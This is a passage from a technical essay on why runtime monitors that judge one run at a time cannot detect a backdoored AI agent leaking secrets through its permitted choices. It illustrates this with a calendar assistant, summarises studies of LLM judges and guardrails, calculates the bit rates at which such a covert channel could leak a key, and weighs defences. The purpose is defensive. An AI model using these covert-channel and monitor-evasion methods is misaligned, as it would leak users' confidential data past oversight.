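Actions that a policy allows can still cause harm, and some of that harm does not show up in any single run. Suppose an assistant is allowed to offer colleagues any free slot in its user's calendar. Offering a slot is harmless if the assistant picked it for convenience, but it is a leak if the assistant picked it because the user has a confidential interview that day. Most runtime shields check one run at a time, and people disagree about how much that matters.

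### An offer that depends on a secret

The example comes from Pandey, Jain and colleagues (2026), in *Local Allow, Global Deny*. A user asks a scheduling assistant to find a time for a team meeting and allows it to share which slots are free. The assistant can read the whole calendar, including why each busy slot is busy, but it may not reveal those reasons. Two of its possible runs are:

| | Run A | Run B |
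|---|---|---|
| Free slots | 10 and 11 | 10 and 11 |
| Reason another slot is busy | Ordinary meeting | Confidential interview |
| Slot offered | 10 | 11 |

Both slots are free, so either offer is permitted. But anyone who knows the assistant's habit can infer the interview from the offer of slot 11. If the model is compromised, whoever corrupted its training could have chosen that habit.

The assistant has violated noninterference, the requirement that secret inputs not affect public outputs. Showing a violation requires two runs with the same public inputs but different secrets and different public outputs. This makes noninterference a hyperproperty, like the earlier rule that commit messages must reveal nothing about the database password.

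Strict noninterference would forbid the assistant to reveal even which slots are free, so Pandey and colleagues use a relaxed version. For a run t, let low(t) be the public inputs, hi(t) the private data and obs(t) what the assistant discloses. The policy supplies two functions. D picks out the private data that the assistant may reveal, which here is whether each slot is free. α picks out the parts of a disclosure that matter, such as the slots offered and the recipient. The agent complies if every two of its possible runs, t and t′, satisfy this condition:

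If low(t) = low(t′) and D(hi(t)) = D(hi(t′)), then α(obs(t)) = α(obs(t′)).

Runs A and B agree on everything before "then" but differ in the slot offered, so together they break the rule.

### Why a monitor without false alarms catches nothing

Pandey and colleagues prove that if a monitor judges each run separately and never raises a false alarm, it cannot detect any violation of this rule:

1. Take any run t, and consider an agent whose only possible run is t. The rule can compare t only with itself, so this agent complies.
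2. The monitor never raises a false alarm, so it must let t through.
3. Because t could be any run, the monitor lets every run through, including A and B.

The proof does not depend on how the monitor decides, so replacing it with a more capable model would not help. Information-flow labels help only if the monitor treats everything the assistant writes after reading the calendar as secret, but then it also blocks harmless offers.

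A monitor that is allowed to raise false alarms can do better if leaking runs look unusual. *The Oversight Gap* (Xu, 2026) measures a monitor's performance by balanced accuracy, the average of the share of leaks caught and the share of clean runs let through. For any monitor that sees one run, balanced accuracy is at most ½ + ½TV, where TV is the total variation distance between the distributions of clean and leaking runs. If TV is 0.4, the best possible monitor scores 70%. If leaking runs look exactly like clean ones, TV is zero and no monitor can score above 50%, the same as random guessing.

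An attacker can aim for a TV of zero. Suppose an honest assistant chooses between two free slots at random, while a compromised one chooses according to a secret that is equally likely to be yes or no. Both offer each slot half the time, so even a monitor that knows these frequencies exactly cannot tell the assistants apart. *Don't Judge an Agent by Its Messages*, by Pandey (a different Pandey), Duttagupta and colleagues (2026), proves more generally that the exact distribution of messages for each task determines how much private information leaks only if, for every task, either the remaining private data or the message is already fixed.

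### When the model chooses at random

Language models usually choose their words partly at random, so two runs can differ without any leak. For such a model, noninterference requires the probabilities of its disclosures to be the same whatever the secret is. For example, the assistant may choose randomly between slots 10 and 11, as long as the interview doesn't change the probability of either choice.

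A single run cannot show whether an agent depends on a secret either. For any run a monitor observes, Pandey, Jain and colleagues construct two agents that could have produced it, one that ignores the secret and one that depends on it. The monitor must treat both agents the same way, so it is wrong about one of them.

Comparing runs provides the missing evidence, but that evidence is only statistical. Xu shows that if changing the secret shifts the probabilities by ε, detecting the shift takes on the order of 1/ε² replays for each version of the secret. Ignoring constant factors, that is 100 replays for a shift of ten percentage points and 10,000 for a shift of one point. No finite number of replays can rule out every leak, because a leaking agent can be arbitrarily close to a safe one.

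### Judges shown one run or two

Pandey, Jain and colleagues tested nine language models as judges of the scheduling leak, running each of ten versions of the scenario three times. When the judges saw one action at a time, eight never blocked anything. The ninth, Kimi-K2.6, blocked an action in three of the 30 trials, but it also did so in one of 30 harmless trials, so its blocks probably reflected general caution. All nine always blocked an obvious attempt to forward data to an outsider, so the judges were not simply lenient.

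When the judges saw both runs together, eight each flagged the leak in all 30 trials, and Llama-4-Maverick flagged it in 17. The trials included no harmless pairs of runs, so they do not show how often the judges would raise false alarms.

A judge might work from an imagined second run instead of a real one. Xu tested this with an assistant that served several customers and sometimes gave one customer another's details. The details were interchangeable, so a single answer didn't show that they belonged to someone else. The table gives average balanced accuracy across six to nine models, depending on the test.

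| What the judge had | Without a comparison rule | With a comparison rule |
|---|---|---|
| One run | 50.5% | 50.4% (imagining the second run) |
| Two actual runs | 65.8% | 90.0% |
| One run and the customer's true details | 68.2% | 100% |

The imagined answer matched the real one only 1.2% of the time, mostly because the judges repeated the answer they had already seen. Even with two real runs, the judges did much better when the instructions told them what to compare.

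### Six guardrails and a live agent

Pandey, Jain and colleagues call the scheduling leak a compositional authorisation failure, in which each action passes its own check but the combination breaks a wider rule, within one run or across two. They divide these failures into eight kinds and assess which kinds six published guardrails could detect.

| Guardrail | What it observes | Kinds of failure covered |
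|---|---|---|
| Approval of each tool call | The current action | 0 of 8 |
| Task Shield | Each action against the user's task | 1 of 8 |
| RTBAS | Labels and dependencies between data | 3 of 8 |
| CaMeL | Data flow, control flow and capabilities | 5 of 8 |
| FIDES | Secrecy and integrity labels | 7 of 8 |
| SAFEFLOW | Labels and the origin of data | 7 of 8 |

All six guardrails miss the scheduling leak because none compares two runs. FIDES and SAFEFLOW also cover one of their seven kinds only by raising some false alarms. The team read the designs without running the code and resolved any doubts in each one's favor. A real implementation might therefore do worse on the other seven kinds, but the theorem rules out a better result on the scheduling leak unless the guardrail accepts false alarms or compares runs.

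They also found a failure that one run can reveal. A live agent running on Qwen3-30B handled a calendar task in which the user had agreed to a limit on total disclosure. Each disclosure was acceptable by itself, but in 22 of 60 runs the total exceeded the limit. A guard that checked each action against the user's purpose still left 20 failures in 60 runs, no measurable improvement. A composition-aware guard, which kept a running total, reduced the failures to zero and blocked none of 120 harmless runs. An agent running on Gemma-4 never exceeded the limit, even without a guard.

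Supporters of single-run monitors can fairly cite this result. Many failures that seem to require a view of the whole need only a monitor with memory, like Ray's gate with its counters. The scheduling leak is different because even a monitor that remembers everything in one run cannot tell what the assistant would have offered with a different calendar.

### Covert channels and a count of bits

*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) describes a customer who runs someone else's program on private data and wants to stop it from passing the data to the program's owner. A firm with downloaded weights is in much the same position. Lampson sorts the possible leaks into three groups. The program can leave data in storage that its owner can read. It can encode a few bits or tens of bits in a legitimate message, such as the bill for its services. It can also signal through something not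 intended for communication, such as how heavily it loads the computer, which Lampson calls a covert channel.

Later writers use "covert channel" more broadly. For example, *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (Metere, 2026) applies the term to data hidden in an otherwise legitimate message. The scheduling leak is a covert channel in this sense.

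A choice among n permitted options can carry at most log₂ n bits. If the assistant can offer any of eight free slots, each offer carries up to 3 bits. Someone who knows the code could receive a 128-bit encryption key in 43 offers (128 ÷ 3 ≈ 42.7), and no code could reliably do it in fewer. *Verifying LLM Inference to Detect Model Weight Exfiltration* (2025) gives the general lower bound on the number of messages needed to send a secret of a given size through a channel of a given capacity.

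The attacker needs more messages if fewer slots are free or if something other than the model sometimes determines the choice. But many valuable secrets are much shorter than a key. For example, a single offer is enough to reveal whether a company has agreed to a merger. A model has far more choices when writing free text than when picking from a list of slots, so free text can contain hidden messages that neither people nor filters reliably notice.

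### Blocking disclosure after the model reads a secret

The most direct remedy is a rule, like the one in Schneider's automaton, that bars the agent from sending anything public after it reads a secret. This works for a compromised model if the monitor checks every action, but it would also stop an assistant that had read the full calendar from offering any slot. Costa and colleagues rejected full noninterference for FIDES for this reason, so its proof does not cover what an observer could infer from the agent's choice of calls.

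*The LLMbda Calculus* does enforce noninterference, in a small programming language for agents. Its theorem, checked in Lean, covers every program in the language and any model whose responses depend only on the conversation so far, so it holds even if the model's weights contain a backdoor. Programs can mark untrusted data as trusted, but the paper proves that this cannot weaken the protection of secrets.

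The theorem still allows a small leak, because whether a run stops early can depend on a secret. One such leak is tolerable, but the paper points out that CaMeL retries failed programs in an ordinary loop that its tracking does not cover, so an attacker could extract a whole secret one bit at a time. The paper also reports that, on a set of banking tasks with GPT-5.2, CaMeL completed 67% without its policy checks and 38% with them.

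The firm can avoid much of this cost by never showing the secret to the model. In *SecureClaw* (2026), the model handles reference numbers that stand for sensitive data, and a trusted component controls the actions that take effect outside the system. A coding agent could request a database login without reading the password. Even a compromised model cannot encode a password it has never received. This approach does not help when the task requires the model to read the sensitive text.

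A test of such a defence should check whether the model can still see the protected data after the defence has run, as *AgentSecBench* (2026) does. If it can, a good result may mean only that the model behaved well during the test, and a compromised model might behave differently later.

### Fixing the format and limiting the rate

Another remedy leaves the secret with the model but restricts what it can send. If a trusted program reduces every message to one of K fixed forms, each message can carry at most log₂ K bits, whatever the weights are. Limiting the assistant to two slots would cut the maximum per offer from 3 bits to 1.

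If the task alone determines the correct output, the leak can be much smaller. Suppose the firm requires the assistant to offer the earliest free slot. An honest assistant has no choice to make, so its offer reveals nothing about the reasons. Pandey, Duttagupta and colleagues also analyze an assistant that sometimes breaks such a rule. If its output differs from the correct one with probability ε, someone guessing an evenly balanced yes-or-no secret will be right with probability at most ½ + ε, even if the model and the receiver share a key. In their test, a model sent incident reports to one of 16 destinations and was wrong about 1.4% of the time. After a program reduced its messages to the destination alone, each message could reveal at most 0.028 bits about the secret.

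A compromised model can raise ε by giving wrong answers on purpose, so its leak would be limited to log₂ 16, or 4 bits, rather than 0.028 bits. To get the smaller limit, the firm needs a trusted program that can check the answer, as it could if the answer were the earliest free slot. But then the trusted program might as well choose the slot itself. Lampson proposed something similar for the bill, which the customer could calculate from a published price list instead of letting the untrusted program write it.

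Even when the message format is fixed, a model can signal through the timing and number of its messages. Metere describes a monitor that gives each destination a budget of bits, which refills at a fixed rate. When the budget runs out, the monitor delays or blocks suspicious messages. With free text, the monitor has to estimate how much hidden information a message might carry, and a compromised model may hide more than the estimate. If the model must choose from a fixed menu of options, the firm can calculate exactly how much information each message's content can carry. Consensus sampling's limit of about 3.5 bits per response could also count towards such a budget.

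Suppose the firm allows five offers a day, each carrying up to 3 bits. A 128-bit key could then leak in nine days. Replacing the key every week would not be enough, because by then the attacker could have 105 bits and would need to try only about eight million possibilities for the rest. Replacing it every day would leave 113 bits unknown, far too many to guess. But no practical rate protects a one-bit secret because, as Metere concedes, an agent can always leak one bit by choosing whether to send a message.

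Timing is harder to control. According to lecture slides from Purdue University, Steven Lipner concluded in a 1975 reply to Lampson that a system could close the storage and legitimate channels with little overhead, but that closing the covert channels seemed to carry an unreasonable performance penalty. Lampson had already suggested limiting the covert channels' capacity as a less demanding option for customers who could accept some leakage.

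### Comparing runs

A firm can also run the assistant again with a different secret and compare the results, but it has to decide which differences matter. In one of Xu's tests, monitors that compared only the requested detail caught 99.7% of leaks in that detail but only 1.4% of leaks elsewhere in the answer. Monitors that compared everything caught 90.4% of the leaks elsewhere but flagged 75.7% of clean traffic, because honest answers vary in wording.

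Pandey, Jain and colleagues had this problem in their first audit of Claude Sonnet 4.6. They mistook a difference in phrasing for a significant hidden signal in the model's offers, although it had offered the same slots in both conditions. After they corrected the analysis, they found no leaks in 80 trials, which is compatible with a true rate of up to 3.7%.

This kind of audit can miss a compromised model. The trigger may be missing from every test, and Xu warns that a system that detects it is being probed can behave well on the probes. The firm could instead replay each live request with a substitute secret, so both runs contain any trigger in the request itself. It would still need many replays to distinguish a weak signal from ordinary variation.

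Deliberate underperformance is similarly hard to detect from a single run. A poor security review does not show whether the model could have done better, and the natural evidence would be another run in which it did. Xu suggests that deliberate underperformance, like a leak, has to be identified by comparing two runs, but did not test this.

### One copy for each level of secrecy

The remaining remedy runs a separate copy of the program for each level of secrecy. In 2010, Devriese and Piessens, in *Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution*, proposed this for untrusted code in web browsers. With two levels, it works as follows:

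1. The public copy receives the public inputs, with a default value in place of each secret.
2. The secret copy receives everything.
3. Only the public copy can send public output. The system discards any public output from the secret copy.

The public copy never receives the secret, so nothing it sends can depend on the secret. This holds for any program, even a hostile one. It does not contradict the theorem about single-run monitors, because the system controls the program's input instead of checking its behavior. *Transparent IFC Enforcement* (2020) gives the general definition, in which the program runs once for each label, on input censored to what that label permits.

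The scheduling assistant's public copy would receive only the list of free slots. It would receive the same input in runs A and B, so the interview could not affect which slots it offers. The secret copy could read the full calendar and write private notes for the user.

Devriese and Piessens proved that a program that already satisfies noninterference behaves exactly as before whenever it would normally finish. Their proof is for a simple programming language without randomness, so it does not apply directly to language models. If the two copies of the assistant each chose a slot at random, the secret copy might tell the user about slot 10 after the public copy had offered slot 11. The firm can prevent this by showing the public copy's messages to the secret copy, because information is allowed to flow from public to secret.

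In browser tests with two levels, running the copies one after the other at least doubled the running time on most benchmarks. Running them in parallel on two processor cores added 2% to 25% to the time and used 50% to 100% more memory. A language model would need roughly one extra run for each additional level. The firm also loses any benefit from letting the secret influence the public message. For example, the public copy would not know about a stressful interview, so it could not avoid offering the slot straight after it.

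This method gives the strongest protection of secrets from a compromised model, but it requires real separation between the copies. The public copy must never wait for the secret one, because its timing could reveal something, and it must never read files that the secret copy has written. Lampson wrote in 1973 that a confined program must likewise keep no memory between calls. If a supplier runs the model on its own servers, the firm cannot verify that the public copy meets either condition.

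Separate copies of the coding agent also protect only secrets. A public copy that has never read the credentials file can still put a flaw in the code it writes.
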